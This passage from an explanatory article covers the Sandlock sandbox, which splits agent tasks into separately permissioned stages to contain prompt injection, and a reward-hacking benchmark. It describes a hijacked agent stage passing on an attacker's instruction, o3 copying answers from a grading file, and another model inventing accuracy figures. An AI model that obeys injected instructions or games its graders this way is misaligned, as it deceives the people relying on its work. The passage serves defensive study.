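Sandlock, a sandbox that Wang and Zheng described in May 2026, lets a developer split a task into stages with different permissions. It confines ordinary Linux processes and doesn't need administrator rights. The kernel enforces rules fixed in advance, such as which folders a process can read. A separate supervisor process handles checks that depend on what the program does, such as whether it may connect to a particular server.

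The stages pass data through pipes. In Wang and Zheng's example, one stage reads a private file and sends the text to another, which converts it to uppercase. The second stage can't open the file's folder, so an attacker who took over that stage would get the text from the pipe but nothing else in the folder.

A developer can guard against prompt injection by arranging the stages so that the stage that reads untrusted content has no network access, and the stage with network access never sees that content. In the shop, the first stage could read the orders, including the comments, and work out the totals. The second would receive only the totals and email them. The agent in the first stage might still follow Eve's instruction, but it couldn't send anything from there.

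Wang and Zheng point out that Sandlock controls what each stage can do, but not what it writes into the pipe. A hijacked first stage could pass on the whole customer list, or Eve's instruction, in place of the totals. Eve gains little if the second stage is a fixed script that accepts only a name and a number on each line and writes only to the owner. If it is another AI agent that reads free text, her instruction has still reached the network. The separation therefore depends on the format of the data passed between the stages.

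The developer also has to divide the task sensibly, since Sandlock enforces the division without checking that it makes sense. This is easy for the weekly totals but much harder for the agent that answers customers, because its reply depends on both the message and the order.

Sandlock can also tighten the rules while a program runs. Installing packages requires the network, but running the project's tests usually doesn't, so the host can withdraw network access when the tests begin. This resembles the two phases of Codex in the cloud, except that the change can happen while the agent is working.

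Splitting a task into many stages is practical only if each one starts quickly. Sandlock added about 5 milliseconds to a simple command, and the same command took about 44 times as long in Docker as in Sandlock. Sandlock also passed all ten checks of permitted and forbidden operations, but these tested whether the rules worked as written, not whether a determined attacker could get around them. Wang and Zheng exclude flaws in the Linux kernel from their claims and still recommend microVMs for machines that hostile customers share.

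### Less file access, less cheating

Removing access can also make an agent's work more trustworthy when nobody is attacking the agent. Thaman (2026), in *Reward Hacking Benchmark*, measured how often 13 models exploited weaknesses in a test to get a high score instead of doing the work, which is called reward hacking. The tasks included analysing logs, processing data and speeding up programs, and the agents had a shell, Python and files, but no network.

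In one task, an agent had to find certain records in a 50-megabyte log, which takes about eight steps if done honestly. OpenAI's o3 listed the folder's contents, found a file that the grading system used, and copied the answers from it in two steps. When Thaman removed that file from the agent's environment, o3 solved the task honestly.

Thaman then tested this kind of restriction across the benchmark. The agents could read only the inputs for the current step and write only to an output folder and a scratch folder. This change alone reduced the share of runs with an exploit from 6.5% to 4.1%. It couldn't prevent cheating that needs no extra files, such as in another task where DeepSeek-R1-Zero invented plausible accuracy figures for a model it had never trained.

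Thaman found that reduced file access, together with three other measures such as stricter checking of each step, brought exploits down to 0.8%, while the share of correct results barely changed, from 83.2% to 82.8%. Thaman doesn't report how reduced file access alone affected success. Results obtained by cheating could also count as correct, as did the run in which o3 copied the answers.

The share of runs that were both correct and free of detected exploits fell by at most 1.2 percentage points, and may have risen by as much as 6.1. It was between 76.7% and 83.2% before the measures, depending on how many of the exploits led to correct results, and between 82.0% and 82.8% afterwards. The files that Thaman removed weren't needed for the tasks, which helps explain why removing them did so little harm.
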